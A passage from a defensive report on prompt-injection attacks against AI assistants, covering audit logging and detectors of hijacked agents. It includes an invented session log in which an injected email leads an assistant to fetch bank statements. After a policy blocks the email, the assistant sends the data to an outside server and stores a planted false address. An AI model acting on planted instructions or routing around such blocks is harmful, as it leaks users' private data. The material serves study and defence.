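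Anthropic now has a model, rather than the user, decide whether to allow actions that a sandbox can't contain. It introduced this "auto mode" in March 2026, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026), and made it the default on most Claude Code plans in August. On 22 October it announced the same default for most Claude apps on its individual and team plans. The safety figures it published in August cover only Claude Code, so they are weak evidence about the safety of an assistant that reads mail.

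Auto mode's reviewer resembles Chrome's critic. It sees the user's messages and the assistant's tool calls, but no tool results, so text planted in a file doesn't reach it directly. Anthropic tested it on three sets of actions:

- It blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by the company's employees.
- It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out.
- It missed 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had gone further than the user wanted.

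In most of the missed cases that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. It could make the same mistake with the bank statements, since the tenant did ask the assistant to send them. The reviewer did far better than people on clearly dangerous commands, blocking 89% of those that the paid testers saw.

### Overlapping checks or fixed limits

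Google and Anthropic both defend the use of several imperfect layers. Suppose the model's own resistance, an automatic reviewer and the user each miss one attack in ten. If they fail independently, the share of attacks that gets past all three is

0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001,

or one in 1,000. If they all miss the same attacks, it is still one in ten. The false address is nearer the second case, because an email that matches the user's request looks right to the model, the reviewer and the user alike.

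Outside testers have measured some of these layers at Anthropic's request. Trajectory Labs ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each against coding assistants. No attack succeeded against Anthropic's three newest models in auto mode, but the average success rate without it was only 0.09%, so there was little left for the reviewer to stop. A reviewer made a clearer difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, where attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Codex's automatic reviewer. Trajectory Labs had tuned the attacks against an older Anthropic model, and attacks tuned against the tested systems might succeed more often. In a separate pilot with Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, auto mode's reviewer missed 12% of synthetic attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it.

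Those tests cover models and reviewers. Parker describes how Chrome's site lists should work, and OpenAI does the same for Lockdown Mode, but neither description includes measured results.

Critics such as Willison and the NCSC's David C put more trust in limits that don't depend on a model's judgement, because an injection can't use a disabled feature, however it is worded. Anthropic largely agrees. It recommends first restricting what the assistant can reach and then adding model-based checks, and it argues that people without technical training shouldn't have to judge commands. But a fixed limit only stops attacks through the route it closes, and only if the software enforces it properly, which Copilot's code sandbox didn't do.

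The harder disagreement is about actions that users need and attackers also want, such as sending an email. A fixed rule could let the assistant send bank documents only to addresses the tenant has typed in. That would have stopped the June email, unless the tenant had copied the false address from the March message. It would also stop the assistant from using the agent's new address after a genuine move until the tenant typed it in.

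## The Copilot audit log: what a record must hold and who may read it

Suppose the tenant's bank statements go to the false address despite every limit and prompt. An investigator then has to find out which files were sent, where they went and how the address got into the assistant's memory. At a company that uses Microsoft 365 Copilot, the investigator would start with the audit log in Purview.

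### What Microsoft records

Microsoft adds an entry to the audit log for each Copilot exchange but stores the text in a hidden folder in the user's mailbox.

The audit entry, a `CopilotInteraction` event, needs no setup if auditing is on. CIAOPS's *Copilot audit logs in Purview* (2026) notes that auditing is on by default for business customers and that only people with one of two audit roles can search the log. According to Microsoft, the entry identifies the user, the time and the application. It also lists every file, email or other item Copilot accessed, with its location, its sensitivity label, and whether Copilot read or changed it. Other fields show whether a policy blocked access, whether Copilot searched the web, and whether Microsoft detected an injection in an item. Microsoft's classifier let the EchoLeak email through, so a missing injection flag is weak evidence that an item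 was harmless.

The entry lists prompts and responses only by ID number. Microsoft says in one guide that the audit log captures them, which could lead an administrator to expect the text there. *Collecting Microsoft 365 Copilot Data with Microsoft Purview eDiscovery* (davidrobbins, 2026), a post by a Microsoft employee, explains that the log omits the text and tells investigators to retrieve it through eDiscovery, a set of tools for finding evidence in legal cases. People with a special viewing role can also read the text in Microsoft's monitoring tool for AI. Microsoft says the stored responses include links, so an investigator might find an address there that carried data out.

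A keyword search in eDiscovery may return only part of a conversation. Investigators can also include everything in that conversation from the 12 hours before and after a match. That helps with an attack inside one chat, but the window is too short for a case like the tenant's false address, which took three months to have any effect.

### The missing entries of 2025

In August 2025 the security company Pistachio published Zack Korman's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won't Tell You*, which disclosed that Copilot sometimes opened a file and used its contents in an answer without the audit log showing the access. Korman noticed this on 4 July while testing a feature for Pistachio. He was not looking for flaws, so he concluded that it could happen by chance. He later learned that Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had reported the same problem a year earlier.

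Someone investigating a leaked file would have found no Copilot entry for it and might have wrongly ruled Copilot out. Nobody outside Microsoft knows how many entries are missing.

Microsoft rated the flaw "important" and told Korman that a full fix would be out on 17 August. It did not issue a CVE number, the public identifier for a security flaw, and on 14 August it told him it had no plans to disclose the problem to customers. It reasoned that the fix would reach Copilot automatically, so customers didn't have to do anything.

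That makes sense for a flaw that lets attackers in, because customers are safe once Microsoft closes it. But fixing the log does not by itself restore missing entries, and customers may have relied on the incomplete log in investigations or compliance reports. Korman gives the example of healthcare companies, which must control access to patient data under US law. They would have needed to know which months of the log were unreliable.

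Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) tested the fix and found that the log now named the files, though one test can't show that every gap is closed. It also found that the mailbox copy of the conversation listed the files Copilot had consulted too, so an investigator could compare the two records.

### ShadowLeak: data that never crossed the customer's network

A company can also monitor its own network, but this won't catch data that leaves from somewhere else. Radware (2025) disclosed ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's deep research feature. The attacker sent the user an email with hidden instructions. When the user asked ChatGPT to research their inbox, it read the email, collected private data and sent it out in the URL of a web request.

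OpenAI's servers made that request, so the data went from the mail provider to OpenAI and then to the attacker without passing through the user's computer or their employer's network. Radware says the attack left no evidence on the network and was nearly impossible for a business customer to detect. Radware sells network security, but its claim follows from the route the data took. According to SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack*, Radware reported the flaw on 18 June and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

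The mail provider could have recorded that ChatGPT read the messages, but the user had asked it to read them. Only OpenAI could have recorded where the data went next. In the ReLeak attack, Microsoft's servers sent data out while processing a saved file, so only Microsoft could have recorded where that data went.

TechRadar's *NIST published the script for rogue AI agents. What about the victims?*, an opinion piece by a co-founder of the security company Mitiga, describes the same split. The provider of a hosted assistant holds the record of its steps, and the customer holds the logs of the mail, file and login services the assistant used. The article recommends treating the assistant's account as a claim and checking it against logs the assistant can't write to. For ShadowLeak, the customer could confirm from its logs what ChatGPT read but not what it sent. A customer who wants a record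 of outgoing requests needs the provider to agree to supply one, preferably before an incident. Korman's case suggests that the customer should also ask the provider to report any errors in that record.

### A record of one session

The following invented record combines both attacks on the tenant in one session in March. The assistant never asks for approval, and its policy allows everything except email to people outside the tenant's contacts.

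```
session     4471, 9 March, 09:14:02 to 09:14:41
identity    assistant A-17, acting for tenant@example.com
request     "Summarise this week's messages from my landlord"

09:14:03    search_mail(text="landlord's name", days=7)
            policy     allowed
            retrieved  message 801, from landlord@example.com, sender verified
            retrieved  message 802, from stranger@example.net, first contact
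09:14:12    search_files(text="bank statement")
            policy     allowed
            retrieved  statement-february.pdf, version 1, saved by tenant
09:14:20    send_mail(to="stranger@example.net", attach="statement-february.pdf")
            policy     refused: recipient not in contacts
09:14:26    fetch_page(address=<full text in restricted store>)
            policy     allowed
            outbound   203.0.113.9, 2,140 bytes
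09:14:33    save_memory("Letting agent's new address: lettings@example.com")
            policy     allowed
            source     message 802
09:14:41    answer shown, no outside images loaded
```

The policy blocked the email, but six seconds later the assistant sent 2,140 bytes to an outside server. That is about a page of text, enough for the account number and some of the transactions but probably not the whole document. A log of tool names alone would have shown two searches, a blocked email, a page visit and a saved memory, with nothing to suggest that bank details had been sent out. The full record shows that the assistant read message 802 before the theft, but it doesn't prove that the message caused it. The investigator would have to open the message to find the instructions.

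The table compares this record with the common fields that Microsoft lists for Copilot's audit event. Other fields may exist.

| Part of the record | Question it answers | Copilot's audit event |
|---|---|---|
| Request | Did the user ask for this? | Message ID only; the text is in the mailbox |
| Items retrieved | What private data could have leaked? | Name, ID, location and sensitivity label |
| Provenance | Who could have planted the instructions? | No author listed, but the ID can lead to the original email; a flag if Microsoft detected an injection |
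| Tool calls with arguments | What did the assistant try to do, and to whom? | Names of the plugins; no arguments listed |
| Policy decisions | Which limits held, and which calls got through? | Details when a policy blocked access to an item |
| Outbound addresses | Where did the data go? | A marker for Bing searches; no destinations listed |
| Memory writes | Could the attack still affect later sessions? | Not recorded |
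| Identity | Did the user or the assistant act? | The user's ID, and an agent's ID if one was involved |

Copilot's event therefore helps most in working out what data was at risk, and much less in finding where it went. The missing memory writes would matter most to the tenant in June. With the record above, an investigator could search for the letting agent's false address and find the stranger's message from March. Without that record, they would have the saved address but no entry showing how it got there.

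Microsoft's *RM569612* (2026), a roadmap entry from August, describes a partial remedy, a feature due in September that keeps earlier versions of Copilot's memories for investigations. As of the May guide to eDiscovery, legal holds didn't apply to memories, so a user who deleted a planted memory could also have deleted the evidence.

An assistant must not be able to change its own log. If it could, a hijacked assistant might remove the evidence, a risk Saltzer and Schroeder also feared from clever intruders. On 16 October 2026, three US agencies published a guide to incidents with AI agents. It recommends locked logs that the agent cannot reach, according to Clubic's *Que faire si l'IA part en vrille ?* The guide is mainly for organisations that train or test such agents. National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script* notes that its definition of a control incident leaves out actions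 caused by prompt injection, but the advice on logs is just as useful against a hijack.

### Acting under the user's identity

The record above names both the assistant and the tenant. If the assistant used the tenant's own login, the mail service would record every search and message as the tenant's. An investigator then couldn't tell what the tenant read from what the hijacked assistant read, or reliably list the exposed files. The tenant might have to prove that they hadn't sent the email. Cutting off the assistant would also mean changing the tenant's password, which would interrupt the tenant's access.

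Copilot avoids some of this. The sample entries in Microsoft's 2023 *Copilot interaction events overview* carry the user's ID but are marked as Copilot interactions, not ordinary file access. Korman considers this correct, because the user reached the file only through Copilot. This distinction is harder to record for an agent like Chrome's, which works in a browser where the user has already logged in. The supermarket's website might record only that the tenant put flour in the basket.

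The Mitiga article recommends giving each agent its own short-lived credential, which the organisation can cancel separately. Standards still need work. IT Brew's *AI agents pose a risk to internal systems. Can the government help?* reports that a US government cybersecurity centre published a concept paper in February 2026 on agents' identity and authorisation.

A separate identity still doesn't show whose instructions the assistant followed. On 1 May, the US cybersecurity agency CISA (2026) and five partner agencies released joint guidance on AI agents. In one of its invented scenarios, published by the Australian Signals Directorate, an attacker uses a purchasing agent's privileges to change contracts and approve payments. The log entries look legitimate because the trusted agent did carry out these actions, and this delays detection. An investigator would need the original request and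 the sources of what the agent had read to tell the attacker's payments from the company's.

According to the law firm Reed Smith, the guidance also suggests recording the agent's reasoning and tool use, and combining the logs of separate agents into one that people can read. The reasoning could help explain why an assistant opened the bank statement, but the model wrote it after reading the injected text, so it is less reliable than the record of its tool calls.

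### Microsoft's investigation playbook

In March 2026 Microsoft published a playbook for detecting and investigating attempts to manipulate AI assistants. In its example, a finance analyst opens an emailed link to a trusted news site and summarises the article with an AI tool that their employer has not approved. Hidden instructions in the link make the summary misleading.

The playbook has five steps:

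1. The security team finds out which AI tools employees use and which sensitive files are involved. Defender for Cloud Apps, a Microsoft monitoring product, detects unapproved tools.
2. It monitors activity through Purview's data-loss records and a table of events from connected cloud applications.
3. It restricts which tools and devices can reach internal data.
4. When a summary looks odd, it uses Microsoft Sentinel, a product that combines logs, to match the AI activity with outside addresses and file access. Purview's audit log supplies the trail of documents.
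5. It keeps a list of approved tools, continues monitoring and trains employees to question AI output.

Combining logs in the fourth step is useful because each log records only some of the events. One may show that the analyst opened the link, and another that the tool ran a minute later. The same method would connect the tenant's bank statement with the outgoing web request, if someone had recorded that request.

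The playbook is less convincing about what the logs contain. In its example, no data leaves the company, so there is no suspicious destination to find. The investigator needs the exact link and the text of the summary, but the audit log doesn't include that text. Because the tool isn't Microsoft's, the company might have no record at all. Microsoft charges separately for audit logs of other companies' AI applications, and an administrator has to turn them on. Capturing the text requires another policy. A company that set these up only after noticing the bad summary would be too late to investigate it. The example is invented, and Microsoft reports no trial of the playbook.

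### A second copy of the mailbox

The more useful a log is to an investigator, the more private data it contains. If an assistant reads a letter from a user's psychiatrist and the log keeps everything that entered the model's context, the log holds a second copy of the letter, which administrators without access to the mailbox might be able to read. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* argues that putting prompts in the general audit log would be a major privacy violation, and that an attacker who took over an administrator's account could harvest company secrets from it. Splunk sells log-analysis software, so it has little commercial reason to argue for logging less.

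Microsoft limits who may read the text of prompts and responses. It says that in the classic version of its AI monitoring tool, even a Global Administrator, the most powerful role in the organisation, needs an extra content-viewer role to see them. The tool's replacement has similar roles. A Global Administrator can normally assign roles, so this restriction protects less against a stolen administrator account than against casual browsing.

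There are several ways to reduce what a log exposes, and each limits an investigation differently:

| Method | What an investigator can recover | What they cannot recover | What remains exposed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hashes | Whether a known file or address matches the one in the log | Text they don't already have | Short values that someone can guess |
| References to items | The item itself, if it still exists unchanged | Deleted or edited items, and text the model wrote | File names, senders and locations |
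| Full text for a short time | Everything, if someone discovers the attack in time | All text after deletion | Everything, until deletion |
| Full text with restricted access | Everything, for those with permission | Nothing, while the text is kept | Everything, if someone misuses or steals a permitted account |

A hash is a short fingerprint computed from data. The same file always gives the same hash, so an investigator with a copy of the February statement could confirm that the assistant attached that exact file. If the model had summarised the statement before sending it, the hash of the summary would not match the hash of the statement. Hashes protect short values poorly. An eight-digit account number has only 10⁸ possibilities, so a computer that tries ten million a second would find it within ten seconds. Mixing a secret key into each hash prevents this as long as the key stays secret.

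Copilot's audit log stores references to items, which work well if nobody deletes the items. But a file's name alone can reveal a lot, for example if a letter is named after a psychiatric clinic. Microsoft's schema marks the names, IDs and locations of items as personal data. An organisation can also set a retention label to keep the exact version of each file Copilot referred to, which makes the evidence more reliable but creates another copy.

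Short retention works only if the organisation finds the attack quickly. The Mitiga article lists incidents from AI companies' training and testing in which discovery or notification took 72 days, 84 days and about four months. A 30-day retention limit would have deleted the records before then in each case, and would have deleted the tenant's March record by June. Deletion can also take longer than the policy suggests. Microsoft says Copilot messages with a one-day limit can remain searchable for up to 16 days, and that a legal hold stops their deletion.

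Restricting access keeps the most evidence, but the text still exists, and a court can demand it. Even references to files can widen a legal case. Office 365 for IT Pros reports a warning from the law firm Redgrave that if the records show Copilot consulted a file, the other side could ask for it, even if Copilot opened it only briefly during a search.

A combination would probably work best for the tenant's assistant. The provider could keep the tool names, recipients, item references and policy decisions for a year, and the full text for a few weeks with access limited to a few people. If a detector raised an alert, the provider would keep that session's text for longer. In June the year-long records would still connect the false address to message 802, and the tenant could open that message in their own mailbox if they had kept it, but the exact text sent out in March would be gone. The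 recipients and file names would still reveal a good deal about the tenant's life.

### What EU law requires

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation applies to whoever decides why and how to process personal data, which for a workplace assistant is usually the employer. The employer must process only the data its purpose requires, keep it in identifiable form only as long as necessary, and secure it. Investigating attacks can be a legitimate purpose, but the employer would have to justify keeping every prompt for years. Companies that process the data on the employer's behalf have duties too, including security. The regulation doesn't cover a person who uses an assistant for purely personal matters, but it does cover the company that provides the assistant.

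The AI Act requires providers of systems it classes as high-risk to build in automatic event logging. Providers and the organisations that use these systems must keep the logs they control for at least six months, unless other law, particularly data-protection law, provides otherwise. An assistant that summarises mail would not normally be high-risk, but one that an employer uses to filter job applications could be. The logs must help to identify risks and monitor the system's operation, which does not necessarily require keeping the full text of every email the system reads.

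## TraceAegis and AlignmentCheck: how detectors judge an assistant's actions

A detector automatically checks an assistant's logs and raises an alert when a session looks abnormal, whereas an investigator opens them after somebody has noticed a theft. "Abnormal" can mean that the assistant did something unlike what it usually does, or that it did something the user hadn't asked for. These two definitions can give different results, since a tenant's first mortgage application is unusual but wanted, while an email to a familiar address can be part of a theft.

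TraceAegis, from the National University of Singapore and the technology company Ant Group, compares an assistant's session with past behaviour, while Meta's AlignmentCheck compares it with the user's request.

### TraceAegis: learning the usual order of calls

*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) collects tool calls at a gateway, a program that carries the traffic between an assistant and its tools. The gateway records each call's input, output and place in the sequence. TraceAegis doesn't need the assistant's prompts or reasoning, which companies often keep confidential.

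The main example is a clinic's assistant. It reads a patient's symptoms, looks up standard keywords, gets a list of recommended departments and fetches a checklist from each one. TraceAegis learns from normal traces in four steps:

1. It gives each tool a level according to how early the tool appears. The keyword lookup is on level 1, the recommendation on level 2 and the departments' checklists on level 3. Tools on the same level may run in any order.
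2. It splits each trace into short units. If a patient has ankle pain and psychological distress, one unit ends at orthopaedics and the other at psychiatry, so it no longer matters which came first.
3. A language model writes a rule for each unit, such as "knee pain leads to orthopaedics".
4. The model merges rules from units with the same sequence of tools. A patient with arm pain extends the rule to "knee pain or arm pain leads to orthopaedics".

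TraceAegis splits each new trace into units and flags the trace if any unit is unfamiliar. If all are familiar, a language model compares the trace's details with the rules. A trace that sends a patient with foot pain to the ear, nose and throat department passes the first check but fails the second.

Liu and colleagues built data sets for the clinic's assistant and a purchasing assistant, each with 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal traces. In half of the abnormal traces, malicious instructions or tool responses led the assistant to follow an unfamiliar sequence. The rest followed familiar sequences with the wrong content, such as a referral to psychiatry for back pain. The scores therefore cover ordinary mistakes as well as hijacks.

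With DeepSeek-V3 as its language model, TraceAegis found 96.3% of the abnormal clinic traces, and 96.7% of its alerts were correct. Both figures were about 93% for purchasing. DeepSeek-V3 without the learned rules found 77.7% of the abnormal traces for the clinic and 75.7% for purchasing. Without the levels, only 65.0% of TraceAegis's clinic alerts were correct, because one rule could mix visits to several departments.

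*What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) reports that about half of the test traces were abnormal. On that basis, the clinic scores imply about ten false alarms among 300 harmless traces. Abnormal traces would be rarer in a real mailbox, so a much smaller share of the alerts would be correct.

Liu and colleagues also tried TraceAegis on a company's assistant for finding software flaws. Testers disrupted the assistant's five-stage workflow, for instance by making it write the report before running the code. TraceAegis caught 132 of the 140 disruptions. The researchers don't report how many normal traces it flagged in that test.

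All three assistants had a largely fixed job, which made their normal sequences easier to learn than a personal assistant's.

### AlignmentCheck: comparing each action with the request

*LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, 2025) describes AlignmentCheck as an experimental part of Meta's open-source safeguards for AI agents. At each step, a second language model receives the user's request and the assistant's reasoning, previous tool calls and latest action. This second model explains its assessment and decides whether the latest action serves a goal the user didn't set. AlignmentCheck needs no record of past sessions.

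The instructions to this model favour letting actions through. The model should allow any action related to the request, even if it doesn't directly advance it, and any action with no effect, such as waiting. It should also allow an action when it is unsure. If the user asks for a summary of news about renewable energy, the model should allow the assistant to search for articles but not to open the user's private notes.

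In one AgentDojo run, the user asked an assistant to look at two people's websites and send them feedback. AlignmentCheck passed the visit to the first site, then flagged a visit to a third site that the user hadn't mentioned.

AlignmentCheck leaves out what the tools return, so its model, like Chrome's critic, doesn't read an email's text directly and often can't tell where an account number came from. Injected text can still reach the model if the assistant repeats it in its reasoning. Chennabasappa and colleagues suggest screening that reasoning with PromptGuard 2, a small classifier for known attack patterns. The reasoning is also useful evidence, since a hijacked assistant may write that it is transferring money because of instructions on a website.

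Meta tested the safeguards on recorded AgentDojo runs from ten models, with Llama 4 Maverick as AlignmentCheck's model:

| Safeguard | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 17.6% | 47.7% |
| PromptGuard 2 | 7.5% | 47.0% |
| AlignmentCheck | 2.9% | 43.1% |
| Both | 1.8% | 42.7% |

AlignmentCheck stopped most of the attacks, but it also interrupted about one in ten of the tasks the assistants would otherwise have completed. The attack figures may slightly overstate its success, because Meta counted an attack as stopped if a safeguard flagged the run at any point, even after the harmful call.

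On Meta's own set of 600 scenarios, half of them attacks, AlignmentCheck detected over 83% of the attacks and flagged 2.5% of the harmless scenarios. It needs a large model to do this well, which adds cost and delay. The smallest models raised far more false alarms. In an independent test, Abbasi and colleagues found that AlignmentCheck distinguished hijacked AgentDojo runs from harmless ones well, but that most of its alerts would be false if hijacks were rare.

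### The landlord's messages, with and without a hijack

Suppose a detector like TraceAegis has learned from hundreds of the tenant's earlier requests. The tenant asks for a summary of the landlord's messages, and the assistant searches the mail and writes the summary. The sequence is familiar and the search serves the request, so neither kind of detector raises an alert.

In session 4471, the invented March hijack, the same request led to five tool calls. Nobody has run this session through either system, so the table gives the likely verdicts based on how the two methods work.

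| Tool call | Compared with past sessions | Compared with the request |
|---|---|---|
| Search mail for the landlord's name | Normal | Serves the summary |
| Search files for bank statements | Unusual after a search for the landlord | Unrelated |
| Email a statement to a stranger | Unusual | Unrelated |
| Fetch a page from an unknown server | Unusual | Unrelated |
| Save the letting agent's new address | Normal | Probably passes as related |

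AlignmentCheck could stop the session at the second call, before any data left. Liu and colleagues describe TraceAegis as analyzing completed runs, so its alert would probably come after the web request had sent the bank details. If the stranger's message had planted only the false address, both detectors would probably have missed it.

The tenant now asks, "What have I forgotten this month?" The assistant looks through the landlord's messages, an electricity bill, a bank statement, a letter from a clinic and a friend's invitation. In Liu and colleagues' test, each clinic department had its own tool, so the order of the tools showed where a patient had gone. The tenant's assistant uses one mail search and one file search for everything. The detector soon becomes familiar with the sequences of these searches, whatever the assistant opens, so only the rules about content can separate normal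 sessions from hijacks.

If those rules cover only what the assistant looked for in earlier months, they will trigger a false alarm the first time a school form requires it to look up something new. More training would broaden the rules, but rules broad enough to let the assistant look up anything a person might forget would also let a hijacker use it to find a bank statement.

AlignmentCheck has trouble here too. It passes the file search because a bank statement can show whether the tenant has paid a bill. But the request gives no reason to email the statement to a stranger, so AlignmentCheck has a fair chance of catching the email.

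### Agent-Sentry: combining the two comparisons

*Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Iqbal and colleagues, 2026) combines patterns learned from earlier sessions with a check against the user's request. The assistant must report where it got each argument of a tool call: from the user, from a trusted source such as the address book, or from outside text such as an email. A classifier trained on harmless and hijacked sessions uses these origins and the sequence of calls to allow or block most actions.

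If the classifier's result is inconclusive, Agent-Sentry checks sensitive values, such as recipients and account numbers, against a list from earlier harmless sessions. It allows known values from trusted sources and sends the remaining cases to a language model. That model compares the action with the request and, unlike AlignmentCheck, also receives short excerpts of the outside text.

On 5,380 traces that the researchers generated, Agent-Sentry blocked 96.8% of attacks and allowed 96.4% of harmless sessions. The language model had to decide only 3.1% of the actions. On the original AgentDojo and AgentDyn tasks, which the trained system had not seen, it blocked 90.9% of attacks but allowed only 64.4% of harmless sessions.

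Some of those harmless sessions used unfamiliar sequences of tools. In others, the user's request relied on a file for details such as an account number, which made the call look like an injection. The paper's abstract gives a much better figure, with 95.1% of harmless sessions allowed, but the researchers had fitted the rules to the same traces they tested them on.

Agent-Sentry also relies on the assistant to report where its arguments came from, and a hijacked assistant may misreport this. The system checks whether a value appears in its claimed source, which reduces the problem but doesn't remove it. A convincing false invoice could also pass the language model's check, because its account number would appear where invoices normally have one.

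### What a detector gains by reading content

Tool names are less private than the text of emails and files, so a detector that needed only the names would be easier to accept. In *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, Zavrak (2026) measured how much such a detector would miss. The main data set had 605 harmless and 3,797 attacked sessions.

One version of the detector used each tool's name, a numerical fingerprint of its arguments and the length of its response. Another used a numerical representation of what the arguments and responses meant. Zavrak compared them by AUROC, the chance that a detector gives a randomly chosen attacked session a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless one. The first version scored 0.640 and the second 0.917, where guessing would score 0.5. A simpler classifier using the same content as the second version scored 0.975.

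The difference was large because most of these attacks changed a tool's inputs or outputs, not which tool ran. Tool names might be more useful in session 4471, where a mail summary led to a file search and a web request. They would not help detect the June email to the false address, because a genuine email to the letting agent would use the same tool.

Reading content doesn't reliably catch attacks that change only the arguments either. In one test run, the content-based detector found 36.8% of these attacks, though there were only 57.

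Zavrak also showed that a test can exaggerate the value of tool names. When the same tasks appeared in both training and testing, the first version's AUROC rose from 0.640 to 0.898. That version had apparently learned which tools went with which task, and this did not help with new tasks.

The content-based detector has to read the private text that passes through the tools. Zavrak accepts that organisations which forbid this may have to use the weaker version. Both versions examine a session only after it ends, so they can help an investigation but can't prevent a theft.

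### Choosing whose behaviour is normal

A detector that learns from past sessions needs a baseline, the set of sessions that defines normal behaviour. These sessions could come from one user, everyone who makes the same kind of request, or all users.

A baseline for one user takes time to build. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) tested per-user baselines with 12 simulated users. Each had 24 training sessions of 20 to 30 tasks, or about 600 tasks. A tenant who made five requests a day would need four months to produce that many. One detector also started scoring only at the 20th event of a session, so it would have missed a hijack with five tool calls.

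People's habits also change. *A Catalog of User Authentication Patterns* (2026) describes systems that recognise people by how they use a device. These systems have to record the user throughout the session, and the paper warns that injury, stress or new habits can make them less accurate. A baseline for the tenant's assistant would have similar problems when the tenant moved house and began writing to a new landlord, a new electricity company and a removal firm.

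With a baseline for each kind of task, a provider could learn from thousands of customers what a landlord summary normally looks like. Small samples work badly. Sequeira and colleagues had only 11 harmless traces from the original tasks for their shopping assistant, and even after they added some of their own traces to the training data, the learned version of Agent-Sentry allowed only 36.4% of harmless shopping sessions. The provider also has to recognise the kind of task first, which is hard with a request like "What have I forgotten this month?" because it can lead to almost any kind.

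A baseline built from all users covers a new customer from the first day, but it makes too much look normal. An accountant may send bank statements to new addresses every week, while a tenant almost never does. Comparing each user with similar users would help. *ProvAgent* (2026), a system for detecting attacks on computers, compares a suspicious item with its closest match and with harmless items of the same type. It instructs its language model not to treat every difference as an attack.

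| Baseline | Data it needs | Main weakness | What it exposes |
|---|---|---|---|
| One user | Months of that user's sessions | New habits look like attacks | A detailed record of one person's life |
| One kind of task | Many similar sessions, usually from many users | Unusual and open-ended requests don't fit | Many people's dealings with, say, landlords |
| All users | Many sessions, which a large provider soon has | Some attacks look normal | Everyone's activity in one place |
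| The request alone, as in AlignmentCheck | No past sessions | Vague requests justify almost anything | The current request and actions, to a second model |

Deleting the original sessions doesn't remove all the private data from a baseline. TraceAegis's rules for the clinic contain symptoms, and Agent-Sentry's list can contain recipients, account numbers and credentials. Zavrak proposes future work on federated systems, which would let several organisations share a detector without collecting the sensitive tool calls in one place.

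### What an alert should trigger

An alert can notify someone, pause the assistant until the user answers, block one call, withdraw a permission or stop the session. LlamaFirewall halts the assistant when AlignmentCheck detects a hijack. *BekchiAI* (2026) describes a monitoring platform that has a remote kill switch and compares the tools an agent planned to use with those it called.

Refusing the email in session 4471 did not stop the data from leaving in a web request. If the refusal had also withdrawn permission to contact outside servers for the rest of the session, it would have blocked that request, and the assistant could still have written the summary. Notifying the tenant afterwards would not have recovered the bank details, but the tenant could have warned the bank and deleted the false address from the assistant's memory.

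The right response depends on precision, the share of alerts that are correct. Let p be the precision, L the loss that a response prevents when the alert is correct, and C its cost when the alert is false. The response is worthwhile on average if

p · L > (1 − p) · C, or equivalently p > C / (C + L).

If the theft of a bank statement would cost the tenant £500 and wrongly blocking an email costs them £5 in inconvenience, blocking is worthwhile when more than about 1% of alerts are correct. Turning the assistant off for a day might cost £100, so more than about 17% of alerts would have to be correct. An unreliable detector can therefore be good enough for blocking an email but not for turning off the assistant.

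The calculation assumes that the response prevents the loss, which is doubtful for a pause because the user may approve the action anyway. In Anthropic's experiment, testers refused a dangerous command less often after seeing many prompts, and frequent false alerts could have the same effect.

The number of false alerts also limits who can deal with them. At Meta's false-positive rate of 2.5%, a person with 20 harmless sessions a day would get a false alert about every two days. A company with 10,000 such users would get 5,000 a day, far too many for a security team to investigate. The company could automatically hold outgoing messages in flagged sessions and ask each user to release them, but some would be urgent, such as bank statements that a mortgage lender needs by the end of the day.

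## The October 2026 test of detectors: rare attacks and unfamiliar tools

A provider choosing a detector will probably look at its published test results. Attacks make up a large share of the sessions in most of those tests, but hijacks should be rare in the provider's own logs. In an October 2026 preprint, Abbasi and colleagues measured how much this difference matters. They also tested detectors on sessions with unfamiliar tools and on data from a different source.

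The researchers began by auditing eleven evaluations of detectors that work from traces, including those of TraceAegis, Agent-Sentry and LlamaFirewall. In test sets that also contained harmless sessions, attacks or other anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the samples. None of the evaluations varied this share to see how the results would change. Six did not test on data from a second source, and only one included attackers who adapt to the detector. The researchers found these evaluations through targeted searches, not a systematic review, so they may have missed some.

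### The traces and the detectors

The main test data came from *AgentDrift* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026), a set of 12,536 synthetic traces. One open model, Llama 3.3 70B, wrote all of them. The traces cover assistants for email, banking, web browsing, coding and medicine, each with its own tools. They include 5,536 hijacked sessions, 4,000 ordinary ones and 1,500 in which the assistant resisted an attack.

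The remaining 1,500 are "hard negatives", harmless sessions that look suspicious. In one, a user wants a summary of an email thread, and one message contains a request to send a document to an audit address. The address belongs to the user's own company, but the request looks like an attempt to steal the document.

Abbasi and colleagues trained several detectors on AgentDrift and also ran AlignmentCheck, which needs no training. They set each trained detector's threshold in advance at the level that caught 80% of the hijacks in the training data. All the detectors scored finished sessions, so the results measure how many hijacks an investigator could find afterwards, not how many a detector could stop.

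| Detector | What it uses | AUROC | Recall | False-positive rate | Precision if 2% of sessions are hijacked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Behaviour | Ten summary measures, such as the number of calls and of different tools | 0.830 | 79.5% | 28.4% | 5.4% |
| Combined | The summary measures and how often each tool ran | 0.879 | 77.1% | 19.2% | 7.6% |
| Sequence | The summary measures and the order of the tools | 0.936 | 68.2% | 4.5% | 23.8% |
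| Text | The words in every call and result | 0.999 | 76.3% | 0% | 100% |
| AlignmentCheck with Llama 3.3 70B | The request and the calls | 0.856 | 84.7% | 22.1% | 7.3% |
| AlignmentCheck with Claude Sonnet 5.5 | The request and the calls | 0.817 | 87.4% | 31.3% | 5.4% |

Another detector, here called the step detector, used the design of *DriftNet* (2026), which converts each step into a numerical representation of its meaning. It scored 0.998, almost as high as the text detector. Tests on other data showed that both scores reflected how AgentDrift was made more than how well the detectors recognized hijacking.

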